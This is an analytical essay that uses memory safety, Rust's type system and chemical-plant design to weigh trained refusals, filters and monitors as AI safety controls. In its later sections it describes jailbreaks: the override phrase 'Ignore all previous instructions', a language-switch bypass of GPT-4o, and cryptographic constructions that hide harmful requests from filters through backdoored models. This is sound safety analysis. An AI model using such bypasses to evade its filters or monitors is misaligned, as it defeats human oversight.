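# Intrinsic versus bolt-on safety controls: what the memory safety transition suggests for AI

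## Memory errors, language models and two ways to control a hazard

A program is memory safe if it reads and writes each piece of data only within that data's bounds and only while it is still in use. C and C++, which underlie most operating systems and web browsers, leave this to programmers, who often make mistakes. Memory errors have persistently made up the majority of critical security vulnerabilities, according to *It is time to standardize principles and practices for software memory safety* (2025).

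Engineers have responded in two ways. Some have moved to languages in which a faulty program either fails to compile or stops before it accesses the wrong memory. Others have kept C and C++ and added defences that detect errors or limit their effects while the program runs. AI developers now face a similar choice. They can train a language model to decline dangerous requests, put filters and monitors around it, or design software agents that have no dangerous actions available. The software record is decades longer than the AI record, and some AI researchers have drawn lessons from it. *Can Safety Fine-Tuning Be More Principled?* (Williams-King, Le and colleagues, 2025) draws six analogies between computer security and the safety of language models, beginning with memory errors.

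### Two memory errors

A program's memory is a long row of numbered cells. When a program needs room for a list, it takes a stretch of cells and keeps a pointer, which is the number, or address, of the place where the stretch begins. Nothing in C ties that pointer to the length of the stretch. Williams-King and colleagues show the consequence with an example along these lines:

```c
int target = 5;
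int array[100];       /* cells 0 to 99 */
array[99]  = 6;       /* the last cell */
array[100] = 7;       /* there is no such cell */
```

The compiler, which translates the program into machine instructions, turns the last line into an order to write 7 where a hundred-and-first cell would be. If `target` happens to sit there, its value changes from 5 to 7, although the line never mentions `target`. The C standard leaves the outcome undefined, so it depends on the compiler, the machine and luck. (A compiler may print a warning about an index as plain as this one. It usually can't when the index comes from a user.)

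The other classic error concerns time:

```c
char *name = malloc(16);   /* reserve 16 bytes */
free(name);                /* give them back */
char *key = malloc(16);    /* may get the same 16 bytes */
strcpy(name, "hello");     /* may overwrite the key */
```

After the call to `free`, the variable `name` still holds the old address, which makes it a dangling pointer. The last line writes through that pointer, an error called a use after free. In *SoK* (short for "systematization of knowledge"), a 2013 survey of attacks and defences, Szekeres, Payer and colleagues call an access outside an object's bounds a spatial error and an access through a dangling pointer a temporal error. In a later survey, also labelled *SoK*, Jacobs, Ammar and Volckaert add type errors, in which a program treats one sort of object as another.

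If the stray values were random, these bugs would mostly cause crashes. But any program that opens web pages, images or messages takes in data written by strangers, who may be able to choose both where a stray write lands and what value it writes. Szekeres and colleagues give the example of a variable `isAdmin` that records whether a user has administrator rights. An attacker who uses an overflow to change it from false to true gains those rights without changing any of the program's instructions.

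More often, the attacker targets the program's control flow. Whenever one function calls another, the program stores a return address, the place where it should resume afterwards. An overflow can overwrite that address and make the processor jump wherever the attacker chooses. In early attacks, it jumped to instructions that the attacker had sent as data. This works because computers keep code and data in the same memory, a design that CSET, a policy research centre at Georgetown University, traces to John von Neumann's 1945 description. Modern processors can mark data as non-executable, so attackers turned to return-oriented programming, in which they chain short fragments of the program's own code.

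A use after free can also let an attacker choose what code the program runs. Many C++ objects contain a pointer to a table of their functions' addresses. If the program frees such an object, the attacker's data fills the vacated memory, and the program then calls one of the old object's functions, it finds the function's address through data that the attacker wrote. An attack can also take several steps. Szekeres and colleagues stress that a single memory error can corrupt more pointers, which cause further errors, some of which leak the addresses the attacker needs next.

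### Ownership and bounds checks

In a memory-safe language, ordinary code cannot cause such errors. Java and Go prevent temporal errors with garbage collection, in which part of the running program frees memory only once nothing else can reach it. Rust, a language for the low-level work usually done in C and C++, has no garbage collector and relies on rules that the compiler checks. *What Is Ownership?*, a chapter of Rust's handbook, lists three: each value has an owner, it can have only one owner at a time, and Rust frees the value when the owner goes out of scope, which happens when the program leaves the block of code where the owner exists.

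When a Rust program assigns a string from one variable, `s1`, to another, `s2`, Rust moves the string. After that, only `s2` is valid, and a program that uses `s1` again does not compile. If both variables stayed valid, they would point to the same memory and both would try to free it when they went out of scope, an error called a double free.

Programming with moves alone is tedious, so Rust also allows a program to borrow a value through a reference, a pointer that does not own its target. Brown University's *References and Borrowing* explains the borrow checker, the part of the compiler that checks borrowing, using a growable list `v` that holds three numbers and has room for exactly three. The program makes a reference `num` to the third number, then appends a fourth. The list reserves a larger block, copies the numbers across and frees the old block, which leaves `num` dangling. Rust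 prevents this by tracking permissions. While `num` is in use, `v` loses its permission to change. Appending requires that permission, so the compiler reports an error. If the append comes after the last use of `num`, the program compiles. The compiler does all this tracking itself, so the checks add no overhead when the program runs.

The rule also rejects some safe programs. If the list had room for four numbers, appending one would not move anything and `num` would stay valid, but the compiler would still reject the program. When a C compiler cannot tell whether a pointer is still valid, it has to assume the program is correct and accept it. In Rust, according to the Rust project's guide to unsafe code, the programmer has to prove soundness to the compiler.

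Ownership doesn't prevent an out-of-bounds access such as `array[100]`, and often the compiler can't either, because the index may depend on what a user types. According to the Rust language reference, the compiler can check a constant index against the array's length, and the program checks any other index as it runs, just before the access. Brown University's *Unrecoverable Errors with panic!* describes a program that tries to read item 99 of a three-item list. It compiles, but when it reaches that line it prints an error message and stops, which Rust programmers call a panic. The equivalent read in C might return whatever was stored where that item would have been.

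According to Google's Rust course, the compiler drops the check where it can prove an access safe, and a programmer can avoid it by writing unsafe Rust. A block labelled `unsafe` permits operations that the language does not guarantee to be memory-safe, so the programmer must ensure that they are. All C and C++ code is unsafe in this sense.

Billions of lines of them exist, as CSET points out, and rewriting them would be enormously expensive. Hence the runtime defences, which work on programs as they stand or after recompilation:

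- A stack canary is a random value that sits between a function's local data and its return address, and the program checks before returning that no overflow has changed it.
- Address randomisation scatters a program's code and data over unpredictable locations, so that an attacker who has captured a pointer does not know where to aim it.
- Memory tagging, a feature of Arm processor designs and the basis of Apple's *Memory Integrity Enforcement* in the iPhone 17, puts a small tag on each stretch of memory and on the pointers meant for it, and the hardware blocks an access when the two differ.

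All of these defences leave the faulty line in the program. An attacker who can write directly to the return address can leave the canary untouched, and one who can read a few addresses from memory can learn the memory layout that randomisation was meant to hide. Arm's four-bit tags have only sixteen possible values, so unrelated stretches of memory sometimes share a tag. Memory allocators can ensure that neighbouring stretches have different tags, so tagging reliably catches an overflow into the next object, but it catches a stray write elsewhere in memory only with some probability.

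### Pretraining, refusals, filters and monitors

A language model's behaviour comes from its weights, usually billions of numbers set during training, rather than from a list of instructions someone wrote. In pretraining, the model predicts the next token (a word or part of one) over a vast collection of text. After each batch of predictions, an algorithm shifts the weights slightly in the direction that would have made the actual next tokens more probable. The resulting model can continue almost any text plausibly, including text its developer would rather it didn't produce, since the collection is likely to contain chemistry and malicious code.

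Fine-tuning then continues the training on a much smaller and more carefully chosen set of examples. Some examples teach the model to follow instructions. Others, as Williams-King and colleagues describe, pair requests that break the developer's rules with the response the developer wants, typically a refusal. Developers also use reinforcement learning, in which people or other models score the replies and training makes high-scoring replies more likely. Weight-level alignment is training that changes a model's weights so that the model tends to behave safely. It makes a refusal the probable response to a dangerous request and a dangerous response improbable, but the model can still produce one.

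Once the model is deployed, the developer usually gives it standing instructions, called the system prompt, and the user's words follow in the same string of text. Nothing in that string strictly separates the two. Williams-King and colleagues compare this to the mixing of code and data in memory. They report that the phrase "Ignore all previous instructions" could override system prompts on OpenAI's leading models for 22 months, until July 2024.

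Filters and monitors are separate from the model's weights, so an operator can replace them or switch them off without changing the weights. A filter is a classifier, often a smaller model, that reads the user's request or the main model's reply and can block either. If someone asks for the recipe of a nerve agent, an input filter may stop the request before it reaches the main model. If the request is disguised well enough to get through, an output filter may still recognise the recipe in the reply. A monitor watches an AI agent, which is a model that carries out a task over many steps by running commands, editing files or browsing the web. The monitor reads the agent's written reasoning, its actions or both, and flags misconduct to a person or to software that can halt the run.

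Developers can also act at the two ends of this chain. Data filtering removes hazardous material before pretraining, so the model does not learn it. At the other end, the agent's builder decides which tools it gets. An agent with no means of sending email cannot send one, even if text on a malicious web page leads it to try.

### From chemical plants to data types

Chemical engineers argued over this distinction before programmers had a slogan for it. In 1974 a leak at a plant in Flixborough, England, caused one of the worst vapour cloud explosions on record. The plant oxidised cyclohexane, a flammable liquid. Only a little reacted on each pass, so the plant had to keep a large quantity circulating, hot and under pressure. Three years later Trevor Kletz, of the British chemical company ICI, gave a lecture titled "What You Don't Have, Can't Leak".

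In *Inherently Safer Plants*, Kletz writes that designers usually identified the hazards of a design and then added protective equipment to control them. He wanted them to ask first whether they needed the hazard at all. They might use less of the dangerous material, a safer substitute, or the same material in a milder form. One of the paper's examples is a device that purifies helium by passing it over very cold carbon. If too much oxygen gets in, the carbon and oxygen can explode. Silica gel purifies the helium less efficiently, but it doesn't burn, so the explosion cannot occur.

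The practice is older than the theory. Another article from the American Institute of Chemical Engineers (AIChE) gives Alfred Nobel's dynamite of 1867 as an example, because Nobel made nitroglycerine safer to handle by soaking it into an inert carrier. Kletz first called the approach "intrinsically safer". The name changed to "inherently safer" only because electrical engineers already used "intrinsically safe" for certain equipment, as Dennis Hendershot recounts in an introduction for AIChE (2012). Hendershot summarises the approach as safety "built into the process or product, not added on", so deeply that nobody can defeat it without changing the process.

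Kletz also distinguished between active and passive safety measures. A water spray against fire is active, since someone or something has to turn it on. Fire insulation is passive because it works without anyone doing anything. Kletz still did not count insulation as inherent, because it can fall off, or a maintenance crew can take it down and forget to put it back. The inherent measure is to use a material that does not burn, since only that removes the possibility of fire.

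Programmers have their own version, "make illegal states unrepresentable". The essay *Make illegal states unrepresentable* credits the phrase's popularity to "Effective ML", a lecture by Yaron Minsky of the trading firm Jane Street (ML here is a family of programming languages, not machine learning). Minsky (2011) posted videos of a version given at Harvard. The standard example, which *Making Illegal States Unrepresentable* repeats, is an address book in which every contact must have an email address or a postal address. A record with two optional fields lets a programmer leave both blank, so other code has to check for the mistake. A data type with exactly three forms (email only, post only, both) cannot represent a contact with neither.

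*Constructive vs Predicative Data* describes the contrast more generally. In its example, a user has a set of favourite people and a set of blocked people, and nobody may be in both. A program can store the two sets and check them for overlap, or it can use a structure that cannot represent an overlap, such as a single table that gives each person one label. Rust's ownership rules apply the second approach to whole programs. Outside `unsafe` blocks, a program that uses a dangling reference is invalid.

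### Intrinsic and bolt-on controls

Three terms can apply to both software and AI. An *intrinsic control* is a safeguard built into a system, so removing it requires rebuilding or altering the system. A *bolt-on control* is a safeguard placed around a system to detect, block or limit unsafe states that the system can still enter. *Prevention by construction* is the strictest kind of intrinsic control, a design in which the unsafe state or action cannot be expressed. Ownership in Rust and the three-form contact are examples of prevention by construction. Address randomisation, filters and monitors are bolt-on controls.

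Other cases are harder to classify. A reactor strong enough to contain a runaway reaction could be called inherently safer or just passively protected. Hendershot says the name does not matter if the design is appropriate, which is sensible advice for someone building a reactor. The name matters more to someone who wants to apply a lesson from one field to another, because the success of ownership rules is weak evidence about a control that works like a stack canary.

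Rust's bounds checks are an intrinsic control, although they resemble a bolt-on defence such as a stack canary. Both run while the program runs and stop it when something goes wrong, and the compiler builds both into the finished program, so removing either requires a rebuild. They differ in when they act. The program inspects a canary only after an overflow has already overwritten memory. A bounds check runs before the access, and it guards every index in ordinary Rust code unless the compiler has proved it unnecessary, so the program never touches memory that isn't its own.

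Whether it is also prevention by construction depends on what counts as the unsafe state. A programmer can write a request for item 99 of a three-item list. In C, the program would then read memory outside the list. Ordinary Rust has no way to express that read, and the program crashes instead, which may itself be a hazard if the program steers a vehicle.

A trained refusal is harder to classify. It resembles an intrinsic control because it sits in the weights, and nobody can remove it without altering the model or interfering with its internal workings. But it does not completely rule out any behavior. Williams-King and colleagues asked OpenAI's GPT-4o, in Japanese, what tools one needs to break a car, and the model refused. When they added, still in Japanese, a request to answer in English, it listed a hammer, a crowbar and a screwdriver. They guess that the safety training contained English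 examples and Japanese examples but none that combined the two languages. A Rust compiler catches a dangling reference even in an unusual setting, because its rules cover every ordinary program and do not depend on a sample of bad ones.

A model with trained refusals can still enter unsafe states, which is half the definition of a bolt-on control, and Williams-King and colleagues regard safety fine-tuning as a retrofit. It is also unclear how much protection comes from the fact that nobody can remove the refusals without altering the model. That property is strong protection in a chemical plant, but it may be weak protection in a model whose weights anyone can download and train further. Whether trained refusals count as intrinsic or bolt-on therefore depends on how much work it takes to train them away and how often a reworded request gets past them, both of which have to be measured.

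## What can be proved about types, monitors, trained refusals and filters

Mathematics can partly settle what a safety control could guarantee, though how often it fails in practice has to be measured. Type checkers, the parts of compilers that enforce rules such as Rust's ownership, have been proved to work. Theorems about monitors establish which rules a monitor can enforce. Theorems about trained refusals and filters show that some guarantees are impossible.

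| Control | What the theorem establishes | What it assumes |
|---|---|---|
| Type checker | No program that passes ever reaches a forbidden state | The compiler and all unsafe code beneath the program are correct |
| Monitor | It can enforce a rule only if every violation shows after finitely many steps | It has only the steps so far to go on, and it responds by halting the program |
| Trained refusal | Every output that was possible before training remains possible | Penalties are finite, and training reaches its mathematical optimum |
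| Filter | Some models respond to harmful prompts that no weaker filter can tell from harmless ones | Certain cryptographic puzzles are hard, and someone has built the model for the purpose |

### Programs that cannot go wrong

*A Logical Approach to Type Soundness* (Timany, Krebbers and colleagues, 2024) defines type soundness as the theorem that any program that passes a language's type checker has well-defined behaviour whenever it runs. The idea goes back to Robin Milner, who in 1978 assigned ill-behaved programs the meaning "wrong" and proved that well-typed programs cannot go wrong.

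The usual proof of type safety treats a run as a series of small steps. The language's rules define no next step for an undefined operation, such as a read through a dangling pointer, so a program that reaches one is stuck. The proof combines two theorems. *Progress* means that a well-typed program has either finished or has a next step, and *preservation* means that it is still well typed after taking that step. Applying both theorems at every step shows that a program that passes the checker never gets stuck. This covers every input and every length of run, which testing cannot do.

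Well-defined behaviour may not be what the programmer wanted. A panic counts as well defined, so the theorem also covers the array accesses that Rust can check only at run time. *Safety and Soundness*, a chapter of a Brown University textbook, calls a language statically safe if it does as many checks as possible before the program runs and leaves only the undecidable ones for run time.

Memory safety is undecidable, meaning that no algorithm can determine correctly, for every program and in finite time, whether it is memory-safe. If we take a program that makes no memory errors and add a line at the end that writes outside an array, the new program makes a memory error exactly when the original finishes. A perfect checker for memory safety could therefore be used to determine whether any such program finishes. This is the halting problem, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm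 solves it. So a checker that always gives an answer and never accepts an unsafe program must reject some safe ones. Rust, for example, does not let a program append to a list while a reference to one of its items is in use, even if the list has room to spare.

Rust's ownership rules forbid some code that programs need. Many low-level data structures need several pointers to data that changes, and so do locks, which let threads (parts of a program that run at the same time) take turns changing shared data. Rust's standard library implements these with unsafe code, behind an interface that ordinary code can call. Progress and preservation do not cover such a library, because they apply only to programs that are well typed throughout. As Timany and colleagues point out, this excludes any program with unsafe code.

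Jung, Jourdan and colleagues (2018), in *RustBelt*, gave the first machine-checked safety proof for a realistic part of Rust. They defined a smaller language, λRust, which has Rust's ownership, borrowing and lifetimes. They then translated each type into a logical statement about how its values may behave, whatever the code behind them looks like. An unsafe library can satisfy such a statement even though the type checker could never confirm it. The proof has three parts:

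1. Every typing rule of λRust is valid under this translation.
2. A complete program that satisfies the translated rules never has undefined behaviour.
3. Each library with unsafe code inside it satisfies the statement that corresponds to its interface.

Jung and colleagues proved parts 1 and 2, which need proving only once. Part 3 must be proved separately for each library, and they did this for λRust versions of several standard ones, including `Mutex` (a lock) and `Rc` (which counts the references to a value and frees it when none remain). Coq, a program that checks proofs line by line, verified all of these proofs.

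The theorem guarantees that a well-typed λRust program is safe, provided that its only unsafe code is in libraries that satisfy their statements. RustBelt specifies exactly what must be proved about a new unsafe library, but until someone proves it, the theorem does not cover programs that use that library. λRust also leaves out some of Rust, including traits (which let different types share an interface), and simplifies the order in which threads see each other's changes to memory. Nor does the proof cover the compiler that turns Rust into machine code. All of these belong to the trusted base, where bugs do occur; Jung and colleagues found a new one in Rust itself while studying λRust.

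*Refactoring and Equivalence in Rust* (2026) describes how later researchers use the type soundness result. They assume that safe Rust is memory safe and focus on whether a program computes the right thing, or on selected pieces of unsafe code. This assumes slightly more than the theorem proves, but it is a sensible way to work. Much of the practical value of type soundness is that it limits the code needing close scrutiny to a small, labelled part of the program.

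### What a monitor can enforce

A monitor observes a program's steps and halts it when it is about to break a rule, so it does not have to predict anything. Many security mechanisms in operating systems and hardware work this way, as do firewalls. Such a mechanism has no information about what the program would do later or what it would have done with other inputs. In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider proves that it can enforce only *safety properties*.

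In the technical sense used here, a rule is a safety property if every run that breaks it does so at some finite point, after which no continuation can repair the violation. Schneider's argument rests on three limits on what a monitor can do. It observes only one run, so whether that run breaks the rule cannot depend on other possible runs. It has no access to the future, so it cannot allow a bad beginning that a later step might redeem, because the program might stop first. And it can reject a run only after a finite number of steps.

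One of Schneider's examples is the rule that a program must not send messages after reading a file. A monitor needs only two states to enforce this. It starts in "no file read" and moves to "file read" when the program reads a file. If the program then tries to send a message, the monitor halts the program.

A monitor cannot enforce some other rules. One is "every request eventually gets a reply", because after any finite wait the reply might still come. Another is "nothing about the secret number x leaks into the published number y", because whether y reveals x depends on what y would have been if x had been different, and no single run contains that information. A monitor can sometimes enforce a stricter rule instead, such as a ban on sending messages after reading files. This ban prevents one kind of leak, but it also stops programs that would have sent something harmless.

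A run that violates memory safety does so at a specific memory access, and nothing the program does later can undo the violation. So a monitor could, in principle, enforce memory safety for any C program and let every safe run continue, including runs of programs that a type checker would reject.

*Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider, 2006) defines precisely which rules static analyses and monitors can enforce. A static analysis accepts or rejects a program before it runs. Because it must always reach an answer, it can enforce exactly the decidable rules. It can enforce "finishes within 100 steps" but not "finishes eventually", unless it also rejects some programs that would finish. One example in the paper is a rule that a program must never write to the first 512 cells of memory, which stand for the part of a disk that starts the computer.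 No static analysis can decide whether an arbitrary program will break this rule, but a monitor can enforce it by stopping the program when it is about to write there.

Given the same information, a monitor can enforce every rule that a static analysis can, because it can run the analysis as soon as the program loads. It can also enforce some rules that the analysis cannot. Rust's reputation might suggest the opposite. The advantages that Hamlen and colleagues give for static analysis are practical. It doesn't slow the program down, and it finds a violation before there is any half-finished work to undo.

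They also study a third approach, in which a tool rewrites the program before it runs. The new version must obey the rule, and if the original already obeyed it, the new version must behave equivalently. The tool can insert a monitor's checks this way, but it can also enforce rules that no monitor can. For example, suppose untrusted programs must behave as if a secret file did not exist. To detect a violation, a monitor would have to compare what the program does with what it would have done without the file. A rewriting tool can instead change the program so that every directory listing omits the file. A program that would have ignored the file behaves as before, and one that would have reacted to it no longer can, so nobody has to determine which kind it was. This is close to prevention by construction and works for the same reason, which is that removing an option can be easier than judging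 how a program will use it.

The weakness of monitors is that they depend on their surroundings. Schneider lists three requirements: the monitor must receive every relevant step (complete mediation), the program must be unable to tamper with the monitor, and the monitor must be able to stop the program in time.

For memory safety, complete mediation has high overhead. Programs access memory constantly, and to check each access fully the monitor needs a record of which object each pointer came from, which C does not keep. Schneider notes that processors can do a cruder check with little overhead. The operating system gives the processor a table of the memory that a program may use, and the processor interrupts the program only when an access falls outside it. But ordinary hardware does this for blocks of thousands of bytes, so it cannot distinguish an array from the variable next to it. Stack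 canaries and memory tags also miss some bad accesses. No theorem rules out a complete monitor for C, and existing monitors are incomplete because of their overhead and gaps in coverage.

A monitor can't always stop a program in time, even to enforce a safety property. Schneider noticed this for deadlines, and *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited* (2012), by Basin, Jugé and colleagues, gives the general condition for enforceability by separating the actions a monitor can prevent from those it can only observe. For example, a monitor can enforce a rule that nobody may log in for three units of time after a failed login, because it can block logins. It can't enforce a rule that every request must lead to a delivery within three units of time, because that rule is violated when the clock ticks, which the monitor can observe but not prevent.

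Hamlen and colleagues give an example that resembles a use after free. A service lends a resource to a program and cannot take it back by force. The program signals that it has finished, the service lends the resource to another program, and then the first program uses it again. A monitor can detect that use, but by then two programs have the resource. To prevent this, the monitor would have to determine at the time of the signal whether the first program will use the resource again, which is again as hard as the halting problem.

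The monitor must also be able to compute, after any finite number of steps, whether the program has broken the rule, a condition Hamlen and colleagues take from earlier work by Mahesh Viswanathan. For memory accesses, it can do this by comparing addresses. For AI agents, whether it can depends on the rule. A monitor needs only two states to enforce "Send no email after opening a confidential file", which is almost Schneider's own example. The builder would still have to find every way of sending information out. Schneider warns that a program may have many, some deeply buried, and an agent that can run commands could upload a file instead of emailing it. But nobody has a procedure that correctly decides from a transcript whether an agent has broken the rule "Do not deceive the user", so a monitor for that rule must rely on a classifier's estimate, and the theorems about enforcement give no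 guarantees about such estimates.

### Why a trained refusal never reaches zero

Weight-level alignment changes probabilities. For one common form of preference training, a short calculation gives the exact change that the training aims for.

Let x be a prompt and y a complete reply. Before this stage of training, a reference model gives the reply the probability p_ref(y|x). A reward r(x,y) scores the reply, high if people would prefer it and low if it is harmful. A model that trains on the reward alone may drift into odd text that happens to score well, so developers subtract a penalty for moving away from the reference model. The penalty is the Kullback–Leibler (KL) divergence, which is the average of log(p/p_ref) over the new model's replies, and a positive number β sets its weight. Training looks for the probabilities p that maximise this quantity, where Σ adds over all possible replies:

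```
J(p) = Σ p(y|x) r(x,y)  −  β Σ p(y|x) log[ p(y|x) / p_ref(y|x) ]
```

Since r is the same as β log exp(r/β), the two sums combine into one:

```
J(p) = −β Σ p(y|x) log[ p(y|x) / ( p_ref(y|x) exp(r(x,y)/β) ) ]
```

The product p_ref(y|x) exp(r(x,y)/β) is not yet a set of probabilities, because its values need not add up to 1. Dividing by their total, Z(x), makes it one:

```
p*(y|x) = p_ref(y|x) exp(r(x,y)/β) / Z(x)

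J(p) = β log Z(x)  −  β KL(p, p*)
```

The term β log Z(x) does not depend on p. A KL divergence is never negative, and it is zero only when the two sets of probabilities are the same. So J is largest when p equals p*.

At the optimum of this training, each reply's probability is its probability under the reference model multiplied by an exponential of its reward, then rescaled. Because an exponential is never zero, the trained model can still produce any reply the reference model could, unless the penalty for that reply is infinite.

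Suppose that for some prompt the reference model gives a harmful reply with probability 0.01 and otherwise refuses. Refusals score 1 point more than harmful replies, and β is 0.1. The odds of harm start at 0.01 to 0.99, and training multiplies them by exp(−10), or about 0.000045. The probability of a harmful reply falls to about 46 in 100 million. If the reward gap were 2 points, it would fall to about 2 in 100 billion.

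Such small probabilities are as good as zero, but the calculation above holds for one prompt, and an attacker can choose another. By contrast, the chance of guessing a 128-bit encryption key at the first attempt stays the same whatever the attacker tries. Suppose the attacker finds a wording to which the reference model would give a harmful reply half the time, and for which the gap in reward is only 0.2, perhaps because the training examples included nothing like it. With β still at 0.1, the probability of harm is now 12 percent. GPT-4o's refusal in Japanese, which disappeared when the researchers asked for the answer in English, may be a case of this kind. Safety depends on the probability of harm on the worst prompt an attacker can find, and the derivation puts no useful limit on that.

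The statement that no reply becomes impossible also can't be used to tell a good safety method from a bad one, because it holds for nearly all language models. They compute the probability of the next token with a function called softmax, which uses exponentials too and so gives every token a probability above zero. This is as true of a model that never saw any dangerous material as of one with no safety training. Many systems do discard the least probable tokens when they generate text, which makes some replies impossible in practice, but they do so without regard to whether those replies are harmful.

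This weakens the argument of Dutt, Mao and Chattopadhyay (2026) in *On the Limits of Support-Preserving Alignment and Bounded Filtering*. They call training *support-preserving* if every reply possible before training remains possible afterwards. Their theorem on this point concludes that the total probability of harm stays above zero, but it comes close to assuming this conclusion, because it assumes that training multiplies the probability of each harmful reply by a positive number.

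They then add a filter that may query the model at most q times for each prompt, for example by drawing q replies and choosing one. They argue that for any fixed q, some minimum rate of harm remains, which they call a harm floor. The floor could be extremely low, though. If a filter recognises harm perfectly and chooses among 16 independent replies, each with a 40 percent chance of being harmful, it fails only when all 16 are harmful, which happens about 4 times in 10 million. If the filter may send a standard refusal instead of one of the replies, there is no floor.

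A floor on the rate of harm matters in practice only if the filter cannot recognise the harm. Dutt and colleagues argue on cryptographic and statistical grounds that filters can fail in this way, but they only sketch the arguments. One of their lower bounds shrinks in proportion to the number of queries, so it gives no reason to expect the rate of harm to level off.

They report that it levels off in experiments. They put filters around several models and tested them with cybersecurity prompts and unsafe prompts from PKU-SafeRLHF, a public collection. With a filter that drew several replies and kept the one with the lowest risk score, the share of harmful replies from Llama 3.2, a model with 3 billion parameters, was 42 percent at one query, 28 percent at 16 and 26 percent at 64. For a Nemotron model with 120 billion parameters, the figures were 24, 12 and 9 percent. The decline slows, but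 in all nine combinations of model and filter tabulated, the rate was still 2 or 3 percentage points lower at 64 queries than at 16. For the largest model, that drop was between a fifth and a quarter of the rate at 16 queries. These figures are as consistent with a slow decline towards zero as with a floor.

The measure of harm is a bigger problem. Dutt and colleagues label replies with a rule that looks for features such as step-by-step instructions and exploit terminology, which a strong refusal can override. The rule could mark a lesson on how a well-known attack works as harmful and miss dangerous advice in everyday words. The filters also use keywords to score risk, so the experiments provide little evidence about trained classifiers, which can respond to more than vocabulary. They acknowledge that they used heuristics rather than human judges and that their floors are not definitive.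 The paper's distinction between suppressing a behaviour and removing it is useful, but its evidence for a floor is thin.

### Hiding a request from a filter

The cryptographic argument is much stronger in its original form. *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2025) considers a powerful, untrusted model and a filter that reads each prompt before the model does. The filter's designers may query the model while they develop the filter, but they cannot access its weights, and the filter must run much faster than the model. It must also accept harmless prompts with high probability, so it cannot simply reject everything. The paper proves that for any sufficiently varied source of harmless prompts, there are a model and a source of harmful prompts such that no such filter can tell the two sources apart.

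The proof uses a *time-lock puzzle*, which Ronald Rivest, Adi Shamir and David Wagner proposed in 1996 as a way to encrypt messages so that they cannot be read until later. The maker of the puzzle picks two secret prime numbers, p and q, and publishes their product n together with a starting number r. The solver squares r, keeps the remainder after division by n, squares that, and so on, t times in all. Each squaring needs the result of the one before, so extra computers do not help. The answer is the remainder when r^(2^t) is divided by n. Anyone who knows p and q, as the maker does, can compute it much faster by first replacing the exponent 2^t with its remainder after division by (p−1)(q−1).

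To work through an example by hand, let the primes be 7 and 11, so n is 77, and let r be 2 and t be 10. Ten squarings give 4, 16, 25, 9, 4, 16, 25, 9, 4 and finally 16. For the shortcut, 2^10 is 1024, which leaves a remainder of 4 after division by 60, and 2^4 is 16. With primes hundreds of digits long and a large t, the shortcut takes a moment, while the squarings take as long as the puzzle's maker chooses. No one has proved that there is no other shortcut, but decades of experience in cryptography suggest there isn't one.

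An attacker can use the puzzle like this:

1. The attacker makes a puzzle that takes longer to solve than the filter can afford, but not longer than the model can.
2. The attacker encrypts a harmful request, with a key that comes from the puzzle's solution. The puzzle and the encrypted request, suitably encoded, look like random bits.
3. The attacker hides the bits in an ordinary-looking prompt. A program that generates text chooses each word at random, according to probabilities. If two words are equally likely, one bit is enough to choose between them, and the attacker uses the hidden bits for these choices.
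4. The model reverses the process. It works out which bits would have led to this prompt, solves the puzzle, decrypts the request and answers it.

Since the bits look random, the prompt looks like any other that the text generator might have produced, such as a question about holiday plans. The filter would have to solve the puzzle to find the hidden request, and it doesn't have enough time. A filter that could distinguish such prompts from real questions about holidays could be used to break the puzzle. (Uneven probabilities complicate step 3, and Ball and colleagues handle them by carrying leftover randomness forward to the next choice.) On ordinary prompts the altered model almost always behaves like the original, so testing it on them would be unlikely to reveal the change.

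If the model and the attacker share a secret key, the attacker doesn't need a puzzle and can get a hidden request past any filter that runs in a realistic amount of time, even one more powerful than the model. But a shared key means somebody has built a back door into the model.

A defender could still respond to the attack in two ways. The first is to have a filter reword each prompt before passing it on, which would probably scramble the hidden bits. Ball and colleagues show that this fails too if watermarks (hidden marks in text) can survive the rewording and the model shares a secret key with the attacker. It is not settled how much rewording a watermark can survive. The second is to filter the model's replies. In the construction above, the model replies to the disguised request almost exactly as it would have to the undisguised one, so a recipe for a nerve agent would appear in plain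 words that an output filter could recognise.

Ball and colleagues prove a separate theorem about output filters. For any model whose replies are varied enough, they construct a second model and a standard of harm. The second model's replies are harmful by that standard, but no efficient filter can distinguish them from the original model's replies, even if the filter has more computing power than the model. The construction again hides a puzzle in ordinary text, this time in the reply. The standard of harm is an "oracle" that solves the puzzle and rates the reply by the message hidden in the puzzle. The oracle may need more time than any computer has. It represents the world, where a plan's consequences appear only when someone carries it out. With an easier puzzle, an accomplice with a fast computer could serve as the oracle, but the theorem then covers only filters too slow to solve the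 puzzle.

The theorem is relevant mainly to outputs that are hard to evaluate. Ball and colleagues give the example of a long business plan that cuts costs by quietly steering a company away from certain clients. The theorem has little bearing on a nerve agent recipe, which is harmful because people can read and follow it. When harm is that easy to recognise, they note, an output filter is trivial to construct.

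Both theorems prove that some models can defeat every filter of a given kind, and the proofs construct these models by adding a decoder, or a hidden message, to another model. They do not prove that ordinary training ever produces such a model. Ball and colleagues accept that the prompt-reading model is contrived, but reply that contrived weaknesses have a history of turning into real ones. In 2016 thieves took over 60 million dollars from programs on the Ethereum blockchain through a flaw that had once seemed a theoretical curiosity. That is a good reason not to dismiss the result, though it hardly shows that this particular weakness will appear. A milder version of the attack needs no cryptography. If a large model can read a code or obscure language that a small filter cannot, an attacker can write the request in it. How often this works on deployed filters is an empirical question.

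Much also depends on the filter being weaker than the model. Ball and colleagues argue that an equally powerful filter would raise the question of who aligns it, and might as well replace the model. One possible answer is that a filter only has to output yes or no, so even a badly aligned one cannot itself output harmful instructions.

These theorems show that no filter outside a model can be guaranteed to make every model safe. Ball and colleagues conclude that no such filter can make a model safe, which is a stronger claim than the theorems support. The undecidability of memory safety has the same form, since no checker can judge every C program correctly. Rust's designers avoided that problem by having the compiler reject any program it cannot verify, and programmers learned to write programs it can. The builder of a filter has no similar option, because the filter must work with whatever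 model is behind it, and nobody knows an easily checked rule about a model's weights that would exclude the models in these proofs.

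## Field data on moving new code to memory-safe languages

Type soundness covers only code that a type checker has accepted, and most large companies own millions of lines of C and C++ that no such checker would accept. Around 2019, Google's Android team adopted a policy of leaving most of the old code alone and writing new code in memory-safe languages, at first Java and Kotlin and later also Rust. Android has the fullest public record of such a gradual policy, though nearly all of it comes from Google.

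### Android's vulnerabilities from 2019 to 2026

Android's security bulletins list the serious vulnerabilities that each update fixes. Google (2022) counted the memory errors among them, and Google's *Eliminating Memory Safety Vulnerabilities at the Source* (2024) continued the count. The last column below shows the number of other vulnerabilities, calculated from the two published figures.

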